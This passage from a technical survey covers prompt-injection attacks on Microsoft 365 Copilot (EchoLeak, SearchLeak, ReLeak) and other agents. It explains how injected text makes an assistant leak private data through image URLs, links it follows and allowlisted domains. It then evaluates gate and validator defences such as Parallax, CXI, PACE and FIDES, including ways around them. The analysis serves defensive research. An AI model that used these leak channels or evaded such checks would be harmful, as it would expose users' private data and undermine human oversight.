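Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), the company's record for SearchLeak, rates the flaw critical, although its numerical score is only 6.5. It lists no exploitation and states that Microsoft has fully mitigated the problem. Varonis, like Aim, showed that a leak was possible but did not measure how often the attack would work.

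On 3 December 2026, the team that had found EchoLeak, by then part of Cato Networks, published three more attacks on Copilot. Simonovich (2026), in *ReLeak*, describes all three as zero-click, meaning the victim does not have to click anything. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) reports that the data left through an image address, a link to a saved file, or code. A documented block on outgoing traffic from the sandbox, an isolated environment for running programs, failed. Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026) reports that the image attack again passed through Bing.

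Microsoft patched the three paths between 17 September and 15 November, and the researchers knew of no real attacks. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) quotes their judgement that "too little progress has been made". Each patch may have worked, but researchers were still getting data out through rendered images more than a year after the EchoLeak fix, so Microsoft had not eliminated this class of vulnerability.

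### What the fixes block and what users lose

The most reliable way to close the image channel is to stop loading outside images in answers. If the browser makes no request, no data leaves by this route, whatever the address contains. The block has to apply from the first word of the answer, or it fails as the conversion to plain text did in SearchLeak. Users would lose web images, as well as link previews in messaging apps. Clickable links remain a risk. The first version of EchoLeak used one, which leaked data only if the employee clicked it.

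A list of allowed domains preserves some of these features, but it is safe only if no server on the list passes data on or stores it where an attacker can read it. Teams and Bing both passed data on. Willison's log includes two further failures. The email assistant Superhuman allowed images from a Google domain that also hosts online forms, so an attacker could collect data by having the browser submit it to a form. Salesforce had left an expired domain on its list, and researchers registered it. Each entry on such a list amounts to declassification, because the list permits secret data to go to that domain whether or not the data stays there.

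Some companies restrict exact addresses instead of domains. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* describes a system that lets ChatGPT open addresses OpenAI's web crawler has already found and treats newly constructed ones as unsafe. This stops a model from attaching private data to an address, because doing so would create a new address. The system also treats legitimate addresses as unsafe if the crawler has never seen them, such as the address of a private document. OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* explains that when private information is about to reach a third party, the system either asks the user to confirm or blocks the request and tells the agent to try another way.

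An agent limited to a fixed set of addresses can still leak data through which ones it opens. Anthropic's assistant Claude could open addresses that the user had typed, that a search had returned, or that were linked from pages it had already opened. In July 2026, Willison reported that the researcher Ayush Paul had built a site with one link for each letter of the alphabet. By following links in order, Claude spelled out the user's name, home city and employer. This is an implicit flow, since no address contained any private data. Each choice among 26 links can carry about 4.7 bits. Anthropic fixed this by preventing Claude from following links on the pages it fetched, which also makes the tool less useful for ordinary browsing.

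Provenance checks intervene earlier. Reddy and Gujral recommend that an assistant answer from internal sources by default and use outside emails only when the user asks for them. This would have kept the assistant from using the EchoLeak email to answer a question about leave. It would also make Copilot worse at questions that need both kinds of source, such as whether a supplier's latest quote fits an internal budget. It would not have stopped SearchLeak, where the attacker's text replaced the user's request. Reddy and Gujral compared several defences without reproducing the attack, and they expected this one to fail against the automatic leak itself, presumably because it does not block the image request.

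A confidentiality check at rendering would block both attacks. If the context held secret data, the browser would load no outside images, including any requested through relays such as Bing. The check would work even if the system had wrongly labelled the attacker's text as trusted, because it looks only for secret data. But Copilot mainly answers questions from private files, so most of its answers would lose their outside images.

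## Parallax and CXI: letting the model propose and another program decide

A check at rendering protects only one sink. Parallax, Fokou's April 2026 design, puts an independent validator in front of every tool call. The design requires that the reasoning system cannot execute actions and that the executing system cannot reason about them. Fokou makes the strongest form of the separation claim, that even a fully compromised agent "cannot cause any harmful effect on the host environment", since it can only make proposals. That conclusion depends on the validator, because the executing system will run anything the validator approves, including an action that a stranger's email suggested.

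### Two processes and four tiers

OpenParallax, the reference program, runs on the user's own computer and divides the work between two processes, the agent and the engine, which the operating system keeps apart. The agent process holds the conversation with the language model. A sandbox blocks its access to the computer's files and to the network, except for the model provider's address and a connection to the engine. The engine runs the tools and has full access to the computer. The two processes share no memory and communicate through gRPC, a standard system for sending structured requests between programs. At every launch, the agent process tries several actions that the sandbox should block, such as writing a file, and OpenParallax does not start if any of them succeeds.

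When the model writes a tool call, the agent process forwards it to the engine, where it passes through up to four tiers.

| Tier | What decides | Basis for the decision |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | Written rules | Type of action and file path |
| 1 | 37 text patterns and a small neural classifier | Text of the action |
| 2 | A second language model | Type and content of the action, without the conversation |
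| 3 | The user | A request for approval |

A Tier 0 rule can allow an action, forbid it or send it to a later tier. Actions that match no rule go to Tier 1, where either component can block them. If the classifier flags an action with low confidence, the action moves on to Tier 2. The engine blocks an action if the user doesn't answer a Tier 3 request within five minutes or if an error occurs in any tier.

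The executing side therefore contains models that read text, and an attacker may have written some of that text. OpenParallax's *Architecture Overview* states that the engine never calls a language model directly, but in the paper the engine does so for Tier 2. To defend against injections aimed at the Tier 2 model, the engine gives it a secret string to repeat and blocks the action if the string is missing from the answer. An injection could still get the model to repeat the string and approve the action. Fokou counts Tier 1 as deterministic, and its classifier always gives the same verdict for the same text, but an attacker can look for wording that the classifier accepts.

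The engine also labels data on a four-step scale from public to restricted, using file paths and text patterns. If the agent reads a restricted file and then proposes to send its content over the network, the validator should block the request. These labels track confidentiality, and the implementation Fokou describes has no integrity label to mark an account number as coming from a stranger. The paper also doesn't explain how the engine recognises restricted content after the model has reworded it. A later release appears to use a coarser method, since OpenParallax's changelog refers to taint on whole sessions, which passes from a sub-agent to its parent.

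The last component handles mistakes. Before the engine overwrites or deletes a file, it stores a copy that the user can restore. It cannot undo a sent email or a request to an outside service.

### One proposal from start to finish

Suppose a user asks the agent to add a supplier's bank details to a list, using an invoice that arrived by email. An attacker has replaced the account number in the invoice with another. The agent proposes this call:

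```
write_file(path="suppliers.csv", content="Acme Ltd, account 4471-0092 ...")
```

The engine first checks a built-in list of its own files, which the agent may not change, and `suppliers.csv` is not on it. The paper's sample policy allows the agent to read its workspace freely but has no rule for writing ordinary files, so the call goes to Tier 1. The text patterns there match things such as leaked keys and dangerous shell commands, and a line with a company name and a number matches none of them. By default the classifier skips file writes because it misjudged too many of them, so the call goes to the second language model.

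That model receives the file name and the new line, but not the user's request or the invoice, so it can't tell that the number is wrong and would probably approve the change. The labels don't block the change either, because the invoice is not restricted and the list stays on the computer. The engine saves a copy of the old list and writes the new one. Rolling back the file repairs the damage if the user notices the error before the next payment, but a later rollback doesn't recover the money.

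### The test with 280 injected calls

Fokou first attacked agents running real models. Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Haiku 4.5 and Llama 3.1 8B refused every attack, even without the validator, so these runs could not show what the validator contributed. For the main test, Fokou therefore left out the reasoning model and used a program to send harmful tool calls straight to the validator, as though an attacker had complete control of the agent. That is the right assumption for testing a boundary that should hold whatever the model does.

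The 280 calls fell into nine categories, including disguised commands, chains of tool calls and attempts to disable the validator. In the default setting, the validator blocked 277 of them (98.9%) and none of 50 legitimate actions. The second language model misjudged the other three as harmless: the deletion of a temporary file, a web request to a plausible address and a command that lists environment variables.

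In the strictest setting, the classifier examines every type of action. The validator then blocked all 280 attacks, but also 18 of the 50 legitimate actions (36%). The classifier caused 14 of these false alarms. It had learned from examples of prompt-injection text and mistook ordinary file contents and emails for attacks. If these errors were independent, a task that needed five legitimate actions like those tested would avoid a block about one time in nine. Fokou warns that users are likely to turn the protection off if it blocks them often. The test did not measure how many whole tasks an agent could finish in either setting.

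The 98.9% figure also calls for some caution. The first version of the policy missed credential files and system paths, and Fokou added rules and 17 text patterns after testing exposed the gaps. The reported figures are for the improved policy, so unanticipated attacks may succeed more often. The test produced no false alarms, but it included only 50 legitimate actions, so the result is compatible with a true false-alarm rate of up to about 6%. The written rules, which are the easiest part to audit, accounted for only 43 of the 280 blocks. Tier 1 accounted for 163, the second language model for 73 and the simulated user for one. Tiers 1 and 2 each took about two seconds per action.

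### Permitted actions that an attacker chose

The test measures whether forbidden actions run, so it is evidence about authority confinement but not about noninterference. Testing noninterference would require varying the untrusted text that a model reads, but every case began with a finished tool call and involved neither a model nor untrusted text.

Fokou writes that the origin of an instruction is "irrelevant", because the validator treats a harmful action the same way whether the instruction came from the user or from a hidden line in a document. This helps against actions that are harmful in themselves, but it also means that the validator cannot distinguish a payment the user wanted from the same payment requested by an attacker. The attacker's choice of payee, amount or timing may look ordinary.

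*NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) measured how often this happens with a different gate, which turns a written policy into fixed rules and uses no model to check calls. In AgentDojo's banking tasks, its rules allowed payments only to people whom the user had named or who appeared in the account's history. The attack success rate fell from 46.5% to zero across 288 runs with a Gemma model, and the gate refused every call that tried to pay the attacker. But in 8 of the runs, the injected text led the agent to pay a known payee, which the policy permits. With Llama-3.3-70B, this happened in 11 of 140 runs. These payments came to $41,250, of which $40,000 went out in a task where the user had only asked a question.

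Fokou argues that Parallax goes further than the Dual-LLM pattern because that pattern's privileged model can both plan and act. But in Willison's pattern, the controller runs the tools, not the privileged model, which never sees untrusted text. Parallax's planner can read everything. Parallax also examines only tool calls, not answers, so it would have had nothing to check in EchoLeak.

### Who chose each field

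*Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, July 2026) describes CXI, a gate that checks where the authority for each part of an action came from. It is meant to address what the paper calls authority laundering, in which a value that should serve only as evidence is used to select, authorise, trigger or fill in an action with outside effects. Checking only that a call has the right format does not prevent this, and in each of 192 test cases such a check let the unauthorised action through.

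A protected field is any part of a call that selects, authorises or shapes its effect, such as the tool, the recipient or the approval status. Let W stand for text that an attacker could have written and X for a protected field. The basic rule is

```
W ↛ X    unless    W → D → X
```

where D is a typed release. This is a narrow value, such as a file path or a date range, that trusted code has validated for one particular field. In the terms of information-flow theory it is an endorsement.

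For example, an agent repairing a failed software build reads the build log, which outsiders can influence through, say, the names of tests they submit. The log shows a failure in `src/parser.py`. It also contains a claim that the change is approved and an instruction to repeat it on the production server. The agent proposes a call with four fields.

| Field | Proposed value | Where the value came from | Decision |
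|---|---|---|---|
| `tool` | `repo.write_file` | Task policy | Accept |
| `file_path` | `src/parser.py` | Build log, through a typed release | Accept |
| `content` | The corrected file | Model, after reading the log | Accept if the validator authorises the exact effect |
| `approval_state` | `approved` | Build log | Reject |

Trusted code checks that the path lies inside the repository and within the part the policy allows, then issues a release for `file_path` alone. That release could not be used to choose a server or a tool. No release can turn the word "approved" in the log into an approval, because the approval field accepts only a reference to a genuine entry in the approval records. The gate rejects the whole call if any field is bad. The agent may still quote the log in a comment, but if a bot later reads the comment and acts on it, CXI treats the quotation as untrusted text again.

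The corrected file needs a different rule because it must depend on the log to be useful. CXI requires exact-effect authorisation for such content, which includes patches, database commands and shell commands. A validator works out which files the content would change in the current repository, their old and new versions, and their permissions. It can refuse a change that disables tests or writes secrets, and its approval covers only the exact change it examined. Parallax acknowledges a gap here, because its validator reads the command `python script.py` but not the script. CXI's gate does not judge whether a change is good, so a harmful edit that its validator's rules do not cover would still pass.

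CXI also asks whether the call should happen at all. Invocation authority is permission for one call, at this point in the task, with this number of retries. Trusted code issues it as a single-use token, and a ledger marks the token as spent before the tool runs. The log's suggestion to repeat the change in production comes with no such token, so the gate would refuse the second call even if all its fields were valid. The full condition for running an action *m* is

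```
Admit(m)  ⇒  Fields(m) ∧ Effects(m) ∧ Invoke(m)
```

All three permissions must refer to the same record of the action, so nobody can combine an approval for one version with the content of another.

The rule for fields covers implicit flows as well as copied text. If the log led the model to pick `repo.write_file`, CXI counts that choice as untrusted, even though the name comes from a trusted list. Once a model has read the log, it is hard to keep the log from influencing its later choices. In its strictest mode, CXI therefore generates each protected field separately, from a prompt that contains only trusted information and the releases valid for that field. This resembles the Dual-LLM pattern, applied to one field at a time.

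Whoever influences the log can still decide which permitted file the agent edits. With 1,000 permitted files, that choice can carry about 10 bits of influence, and the content of the edit can carry much more.

### What the CXI experiments measured

On AgentDojo, Santos-Grueiro ran 720 episodes under six conditions, and 199 ended with the task completed safely. That total includes conditions that did not use the full gate, so it does not give CXI's completion rate. The gate let 204 actions run, and the paper reports no case in which a field, an effect or a call got through without authority.

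The other large test consisted of 400 episodes in which an agent worked on a software repository. It completed 231 tasks safely (58%), again with no observed escapes. In 73 of the remaining episodes the system could not parse the model's output, and in 61 the proposal received no effect authorisation. In the last 35 the gate let the action run, but the result did not solve the task. The paper gives no completion rate for the same agents without CXI, so we cannot tell how many more tasks they would have completed without it. Seeing no escapes in the 266 episodes where an action ran is compatible with an escape rate of up to about 1%.

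The models did make unauthorized proposals for the gate to stop. In one set of adversarial cases, open models chose a field value without authority in 196 of 300 proposals. Hosted commercial models did so in 85 of 400, and in none of 400 when their prompt explained the policy. In another comparison, CXI rejected all 20 attacks, while a simpler check on the source of each argument rejected 12. The simpler check could not stop untrusted text from triggering a call whose arguments were all acceptable.

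An escape here means a violation of the policy written for the test, so an error in the policy itself would not count. Santos-Grueiro audited the policy for 24 sinks, which had 149 fields, 85 of them protected, and needed 141 validator tests. The audit found 18 problems, nine of them serious. The 18 included free-text approvals and content that had effects but was not marked as having them. Proving the gate's code correct would not help with such errors. *Agenra* (2026) presents a gate whose core has proofs in Lean, a language for computer-checked mathematics, and concedes that the gate cannot enforce a rule missing from its policy.

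### Why CXI does not claim noninterference inside the model

Santos-Grueiro explicitly excludes "complete transformer-level noninterference" from CXI's claim. One reason is that CXI aims to generate every field from a fresh prompt, but the faster version tested on open models kept the log in the context and blocked the model's attention to it. Attention lets a model draw on earlier tokens when it computes the next one. Even if the field's tokens cannot attend to the log, they may still attend to later tokens that the model computed while attending to the log, and these can pass the influence on. A stricter check also blocks text that the model wrote after reading the log, but none of the checks covers everything in the model's internal state.

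With a hosted model, the agent's operator cannot inspect attention, so CXI records only which text the harness supplied for each field. This record is enough to check how the harness built the call, but not what happened inside the provider's system. The claim covers only what the gate admits, and the gate deliberately admits some influence through releases and authorised content.

### When the right value exists only in untrusted text

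Field-level authority can make a legitimate task fail when the task requires a value that no trusted source contains. *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* (2026) describes a user who asks an agent to send $100 to Whole Foods Market, using the correct account number, which appears only on an untrusted page. The unprotected agent completes the payment, while the protected one fails by design because it has nothing to check the number against. Yu and colleagues encountered the same problem with a bill whose account number appeared only in the bill itself. Their rule blocked both the attacker's account and the legitimate one. Without any attack, the share of banking tasks completed fell from 79.2% to 70.8%, although with only 16 tasks the difference could be due to chance.

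Deriving permissions from the user's request does not solve this. The request "pay the bill, like last month" names no account, so a gate cannot use it to check where the money goes. When Yu and colleagues tested Progent, which writes a new policy for each request, 9 of the 16 successful attacks were on that task.

*ToolFence* (2026) suggests a compromise for cases where the user points to a particular file. If the user asks to pay the recipient named in a certain invoice, the gate can accept an account number from that invoice and reject one from any other message. This lets the agent complete the task, but it relies on the invoice being genuine. A forged invoice like the one Girrens and Wang describe would pass, because the account number came from the source the user chose.

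### PACE: what a check at the last moment can establish

*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) also supports a check just before execution, but for a different reason. It considers an email add-on whose code always calls `send_email(body)` and whose plain-language description tells the model how to write the body. A harmless version specifies a fixed template, and a malicious one tells the model to copy a password from the context. Both versions have the same code, so reviewing it before installation cannot justify exempting only the harmless one from later checks. A gate just before the call can examine the actual text and a record of what the agent has read, and can still stop the message.

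PACE makes two checks at that moment. The first keeps a graph of where data came from and searches it for paths from untrusted or secret sources to a risky effect. If it finds one, it proposes a way to cut the path, usually by blocking the call. The second derives permissions from the user's request and compares them with the call's concrete effects, such as its target and budget use. Unlike Parallax, PACE also applies these checks to the agent's final answer.

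Li and colleagues prove that a chain of influence cannot complete at a given call if the graph records every link in it, the labels on its sources are complete and the cut takes effect. They state that this is weaker than noninterference. The graph can miss links when the model recreates a string in its own words. PACE searches for secrets in common encodings such as base64, but it misses paraphrases, translations and short fragments. A visible refusal can also leak information, as an implicit flow, and the paper proves no limit on how much.

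The proof applies to a strict version of PACE, but the experiments used a more permissive one that can restore a blocked call if the second check authorises it. In an adaptive search against 30 AgentDojo goals outside the user's authority, attackers succeeded 21 times without a defence and never against PACE. The 95% confidence interval for the success rate against PACE reaches 11.4%, and the search did not include goals within the user's authority.

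Another experiment switched on the checks separately for Qwen-3.8-27B, using AgentDojo and AgentDyn, a newer suite with changing environments. The full version in the table also makes adjustments at the execution boundary, such as repairing calls.

| Checks in use | AgentDojo: attacks succeeding | AgentDojo: tasks completed | AgentDyn: attacks succeeding | AgentDyn: tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
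| None | 37.4% | 76.8% | 25.0% | 66.7% |
| Paths only | 0.0% | 13.6% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Permissions only | 0.0% | 64.6% | 1.7% | 36.7% |
| Full PACE | 0.0% | 67.2% | 0.0% | 33.3% |

The path check comes closest to isolating influence. On its own, it stopped every attack in both suites, but it also stopped nearly all the useful work. This is an example of label creep. On AgentDyn, the check proposed a cut for 5,842 of 6,647 recorded calls, because most of what an agent does there follows from something it has read. Full PACE had a much smaller loss on the complete benchmarks, at most three percentage points, so the halving on this AgentDyn sample may not be typical. In both cases, PACE stays useful by restoring calls that the user's request authorises, and each restored call reopens the path from the untrusted text.

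## FIDES: labelling everything an agent reads

PACE's path check stopped nearly all useful work because almost every call an agent makes follows from something it has read. FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft in 2025, addresses this problem earlier, by controlling what enters the planning model's context. Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao (2024) had proposed f-secure in *System-Level Defense against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks*. Its planner never receives anything derived from an untrusted source. FIDES also hides such text, but the planning model can read it when a task requires, and loses permissions by doing so.

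### From a labelled message to a checked call

In the simplest version of the design, the model sees everything. Each tool attaches a label to its result, or separate labels to parts of it, such as the sender and body of an email. The harness keeps one label for the whole conversation and updates it with every message:

```
context label  :=  context label ⊔ label of the new message
```

The model's next response gets the context label, and if the response is a tool call, so do the function name and every argument. The harness passes the labelled call to a policy, an ordinary program that accepts or refuses it, and runs the function only if the policy accepts. The result gets the join of the labels of the call, its arguments and any stored data the function may have read. The harness puts the same label on any stored data the function may have changed, so text cannot lose its label by passing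 through a file.

FIDES has two basic policies. The integrity check requires a consequential call and all its arguments to be trusted. The confidentiality check covers who may read outgoing data. Label creep makes the integrity check severe, because an agent that has read one stranger's email can make no more consequential calls.

### Hiding text behind a variable name

FIDES avoids this by checking each part of a tool's result before adding it to the context. If adding the part would not raise the context label, the model sees it. Otherwise the harness stores the part in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name, which leaves the context label unchanged.

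The model can use that name as an argument in a later call. The harness then substitutes the stored text, which keeps its own label. One call can therefore combine a trusted decision with an untrusted argument, and a policy can treat the two differently. For example, a policy for `send_message(recipient, message)` can require a trusted recipient but allow an untrusted message.

The planning model can use a variable's contents in two ways. It can call `inspect`, which puts the text into the context and raises the label, or it can call `query_llm`, which sends a question and the variable to a quarantined model without tools and stores the answer in a new variable. The second option is enough to summarise three emails and send the summary to a colleague, because the planning model doesn't have to read the summary. This is Willison's Dual-LLM pattern, except that the harness hides text only when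 the text would raise the label, and the planning model can still open hidden text.

### A meeting request in an untrusted email

Some tasks require the planning model to learn something before it can choose its next call. Costa and colleagues use this request as an example: read the top three emails, check whether one asks for a meeting, and if so create the calendar event. They call such a task data-dependent. A task is data-independent if at least one sequence of tool calls, with one final response, solves it whatever the data turns out to be. If solutions(*d*) is the set of sequences that solve the task for data *d*, the condition is

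```
⋂ solutions(d) ≠ ∅     (the intersection runs over every possible d)
```

The meeting request fails this test, because a mailbox with a meeting request calls for an event and a mailbox without one does not. FIDES handles it in five calls:

```
read_emails(number=3)                                    → #emails, hidden
query_llm("Is there a meeting request?", #emails, bool)  → #answer, hidden
inspect(#answer)                                         → true
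query_llm("Extract the event details", #emails, event)   → #event, hidden
set_event(#event)
```

If the answer is `false`, the planning model stops after the third call. If it is `true`, the model requests the meeting details (Friday at 3pm with Alice and Charlie) and passes them on without seeing them.

The last call still technically breaks the rule for consequential actions, because the word `true` came from untrusted emails and is now in the context. The policy therefore needs an exception, which FIDES bases on how much information the answer can carry.

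### What a yes-or-no answer can carry

When the planning model queries the quarantined model, it also specifies the type of answer it will accept. A technique called constrained decoding then prevents the quarantined model from producing anything else, so an email cannot smuggle an instruction into a Boolean answer. FIDES orders the types by capacity and adds the type to the label:

```
bool  ⊑  enum["a", "b", "c"]  ⊑  string

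label of #answer  =  ((untrusted, public), bool)
```

A policy can allow a consequential call after the model has read an untrusted Boolean but refuse one after it has read an untrusted string, which is a form of endorsement with a size limit.

For a Boolean, the limit is one bit. If everything except the email is fixed, including the user's request and the random choices, the planning model can continue in at most two ways, because the answer is either `true` or `false` whatever the email's author writes.

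That bound covers only the plan. The email's sender can still write the event's title, time and guest list, which reach the calendar through `#event`. The bound also covers only one answer. Ten Boolean answers can steer the plan in up to 1,024 ways, but the context label does not record how many answers the model has read, because joining two Booleans in this lattice gives another Boolean. A policy that limits total influence would have to count the answers separately.

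A small number of bits can still cause a lot of harm, since a single bit can decide whether a payment goes out. Costa and colleagues claim only that a Boolean on its own is "unlikely" to lead to prompt injection.

### What explicit secrecy guarantees

The property that Costa and colleagues claim for their labelled agent loop is explicit secrecy. Let *d* be all the data that the tools can read or write. Two such collections are equivalent to an outside observer, written *d₁* =ᴸ *d₂*, if their public entries are the same, even if their secrets differ. Suppose a run of the agent on *d₁* makes a certain sequence of tool calls, and let *g* be the combined effect of exactly those calls. The agent satisfies explicit secrecy if, for every such run,

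```
g(d₁) =ᴸ g(d₂)     for every d₂ with d₁ =ᴸ d₂
```

To test the property, we replay the same calls on data with different secrets and compare the public entries. If an agent copies a salary file to a public page, the replay puts different salaries on the page, so the agent fails. But if an agent reads the salaries and posts "Please call me" only when one of them exceeds a limit, the replay posts the same words and the agent passes, even though the post reveals that a salary exceeds the limit. Noninterference would catch this leak because it compares two complete runs, and the second run might post nothing.

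Costa and colleagues accept this leak because full noninterference would forbid almost any public write after a secret read. They point out that web browsers and TaintDroid, a tracker for phone apps, make the same compromise. Their model also excludes timing and the length of network messages.

As printed, the formula guarantees less than this description suggests, because it treats the arguments of each call as fixed text. Suppose the model reads a salary into its context and writes the number in a public message. The replay posts the same number whatever the second collection contains, so the leak satisfies the formula's definition of secure. The algorithm is stricter. It would give the number the context's secret label, and the policy on outgoing data would then block the message. The paper defines explicit secrecy and states, without proof, that the algorithm enforces it.

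The policy on consequential calls covers some decisions as well as content. Once the model has read an untrusted string, its choice of function is also untrusted, and the policy refuses the call. But hidden text can still influence a decision through properties the model can see, such as the number of messages. In one of the paper's examples, a user asks the agent to add Alice to the Slack channel with the fewest messages. The harness hides every message in a variable, but the planning model can count the variables, and it picks a channel with no messages. Anyone able to post a few messages there could have made the agent add Alice to a different channel, and the context would have stayed trusted.

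By default, FIDES checks tool calls and treats the final answer to the user as harmless, so it would not check an answer containing an image address, as in EchoLeak. Because the answer does have a label, a harness can apply a policy to it, as Costa and colleagues mention. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* suggests treating links to servers outside an approved list as public channels.

### Attacks on AgentDojo

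Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, the benchmark also used in the PACE and CXI experiments. It has 97 user tasks in four simulated settings: an office workspace, a travel service, a bank and Slack. It also has 36 attacker goals, such as sending money to the attacker. For the security test, they combined each task with every attacker goal in the same setting and planted text that told the agent which tools to call. Code then checked whether the agent had completed the user's task and whether it had achieved the attacker's goal.

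AgentDojo has no labels, so Costa and colleagues added them. They marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it, which guaranteed that the labels covered all of those attacks. Nobody can assume such coverage in a real deployment.

With GPT-4o, 152 injection attacks succeeded against a basic agent without policy checks. Against FIDES without checks, 21 succeeded, because the planning model sometimes opened a variable and followed the instructions inside. Hiding text in variables therefore reduces the number of successful attacks but doesn't guarantee that all of them fail. With the checks on, no attacks succeeded against either agent.

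These counts exclude some cases that AgentDojo scored as successful attacks, including 20 for the basic agent with checks and three for FIDES with checks. In some, the benchmark counted a call that the policy had blocked. In others, the attacker achieved something the policy allows, such as creating a calendar event with no guests. In a third group, the attacker planted sentences in the agent's answer, such as praise for a particular destination, which FIDES does not try to prevent.

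The policies in the test were also looser than the two basic ones. For payments, the policy checked whether the decision to call `send_money` was trusted but ignored the labels of the arguments. If a user asks the agent to pay an invoice, a forged account number in that invoice can therefore pass from a variable into the payment. The policy protected control-flow integrity but not data-flow integrity. For emails, the policy accepted a call if the recipients already had permission to read the content, even when untrusted text had prompted the agent to send it.

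These tests used a version of FIDES without constrained decoding, so they don't measure how safe it is to endorse a Boolean.

### Tasks completed before and after the checks

The table gives the percentage of user tasks completed when there is no attack, first without policy checks and then with them. Each figure is an average over five runs.

| Model and agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
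|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, basic | 75.0 → 37.0 | 70.0 → 73.0 | 98.8 → 37.5 | 93.3 → 20.0 |
| GPT-4o, FIDES | 63.5 → 59.0 | 50.0 → 41.0 | 65.0 → 52.5 | 63.8 → 47.6 |
| o1, basic | 70.0 → 48.0 | 82.0 → 75.0 | 96.2 → 37.5 | 87.6 → 17.1 |
| o1, FIDES | 77.5 → 64.5 | 75.0 → 68.0 | 78.8 → 56.2 | 79.0 → 54.3 |

With checks on, FIDES completed more tasks than the basic agent. The average gain over the four suites was 8 percentage points with GPT-4o and 16 with o1. The travel suite was an exception with both models. Many travel tasks use tools that the policy permits even after the agent has read untrusted text, so hiding the text only made the tasks harder.

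A user who switched from the basic agent without checks to FIDES with checks would see the average fall from 84% to 50% with GPT-4o and from 84% to 61% with o1. Part of the loss arose because the models had trouble working with variables, which lowered the average by about 24 points for GPT-4o but only 6 for o1, the better model. The checks lowered it by another 11 points for GPT-4o and 17 for o1.

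The kind of task explains much of the second loss. Costa and colleagues classified all the tasks by hand and found that 5% of the workspace tasks, 10% of the travel tasks, 44% of the banking tasks and 43% of the Slack tasks were data-dependent. They expected even a perfect model to complete only the data-independent tasks under their policies. The limit is therefore about 56% for banking and 57% for Slack, and o1 almost reached both. The limits for workspace and travel are 95% and 90%, so most of the remaining failures there came from the model.

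Many of the blocked banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and do what it says, for instance to schedule a payment. The agent completed some data-dependent tasks by luck. In one, the user asked it to change the password if a transaction looked suspicious. The transaction descriptions were hidden in variables, but the amounts were visible, and GPT-4o judged a large amount suspicious and changed the password without reading the descriptions.

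GPT-4o and o1 were already available in early 2025 and are now far behind the best models. In *APPA*, Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026) found that GPT-5.6 Luna, with no defence, followed none of AgentDojo's injections in 160 workspace runs. Zero successful attacks on this benchmark is therefore weak evidence that a defence running on a current model works. The limits on data-dependent tasks still matter, because they come from the policies.

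### Does the enforcement rest on the model?

Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026), in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, claim that the language model performs all of FIDES's policy enforcement, so an attacker who confuses the model can bypass that enforcement. This contradicts the published algorithm, in which the model proposes a call, but ordinary code computes the labels, evaluates the policy and refuses the call if necessary, without consulting the model. Microsoft likewise describes the policy engine as "independent of the model's judgement". Shim and colleagues did not run FIDES in their experiments, partly because they could not fit it into their benchmarks.

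The planning model selects which variables to open, and the quarantined model produces the answers. Errors by either model can make a task fail or put a false value into an argument, but they cannot change a label. A deployment could still make its labels depend on a model, for example by marking a document as trusted after a classifier finds no injection in it. Costa and colleagues mention this option and warn that such steps can weaken the guarantee.

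Two of Shim and colleagues' attacks are relevant to FIDES, though for other reasons. In their scenario, Jane's agent knows Mark's diagnosis, and his former wife Emily wants to learn it. In the first attack, Emily creates a shared page and invites the agent to fill in its section. FIDES's policy on outgoing data would block a call that writes the diagnosis there, because Emily can read the page but isn't allowed to see the diagnosis. But the looser policy from the AgentDojo tests also allows the call if the decision to make it was trusted. Under that policy, the outcome depends on whether the harness labels Emily's invitation as a stranger's text or as a user's request.

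In the second attack, Emily writes a list of true and false statements about Mark's health and asks the agent to delete the false ones. The agent writes nothing secret, but the statements it leaves reveal what is true. Explicit secrecy does not cover information revealed through the agent's decisions, and a deletion contains no secret text for the policy on outgoing data to block. Only the integrity check could stop the agent, and again only if Emily's request were labelled untrusted.

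The second attack leaked 75.6% of the secret items against a defence that relied on instructions to the model, and 2.3% against FlowSeal, Shim and colleagues' own system. FlowSeal uses ordinary code to intercept every call that writes or shares data, but this code calls a separate language model to decide whether a text derives from a protected record. Replacing that model with automatic refusal cut the share of harmless tasks completed from 72.4% to zero, in a setting where nobody answered requests for permission. Replacing it with automatic approval raised the share of items leaked by the first attack from 0.5% to 24.9%. FlowSeal's proof of confidentiality does not cover this model's errors, so its enforcement depends more on a model's judgement than that of FIDES does.

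### Counting label creep in approvals

Label creep is a better-founded objection to FIDES, and the same Microsoft group has measured it in a second way. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) let a person approve calls that fail the policy check. They assumed the person would approve every such call in a successful run, and counted the approvals.

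The baseline for comparison is an agent that follows the common practice of asking the user before every consequential action. On AgentDojo with o3-mini, this agent needed about 48 approvals across all the tasks and completed 24.3% of the tasks without any. Adding labels and asking only when a check failed reduced the approvals to about 32. FIDES needed about 19 and completed 50.1% of the tasks without any approvals. FIDES therefore saves the user effort compared with an agent that always asks, though it restricts the user more than an agent that acts freely.

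Kolluri and colleagues then built Prudentia, a version of FIDES that gives the planning model information about the labels and policies so it can plan around them. Prudentia completed 59.1% of the tasks without approval. With another model, o4-mini, Prudentia needed about half as many approvals as FIDES (19 versus 37) and completed slightly fewer tasks overall (73.2% versus 75.7%).

Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a whole text. If an email contains a to-do list with ten items, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten separate calls. This is less secure, because the agent then treats everything in the email as trusted. If the user overlooks an eleventh item from an attacker, the label check will no longer stop the agent from acting on it. Kolluri and colleagues measured approvals only in runs without attacks, so they did not measure how often users would make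 this mistake.

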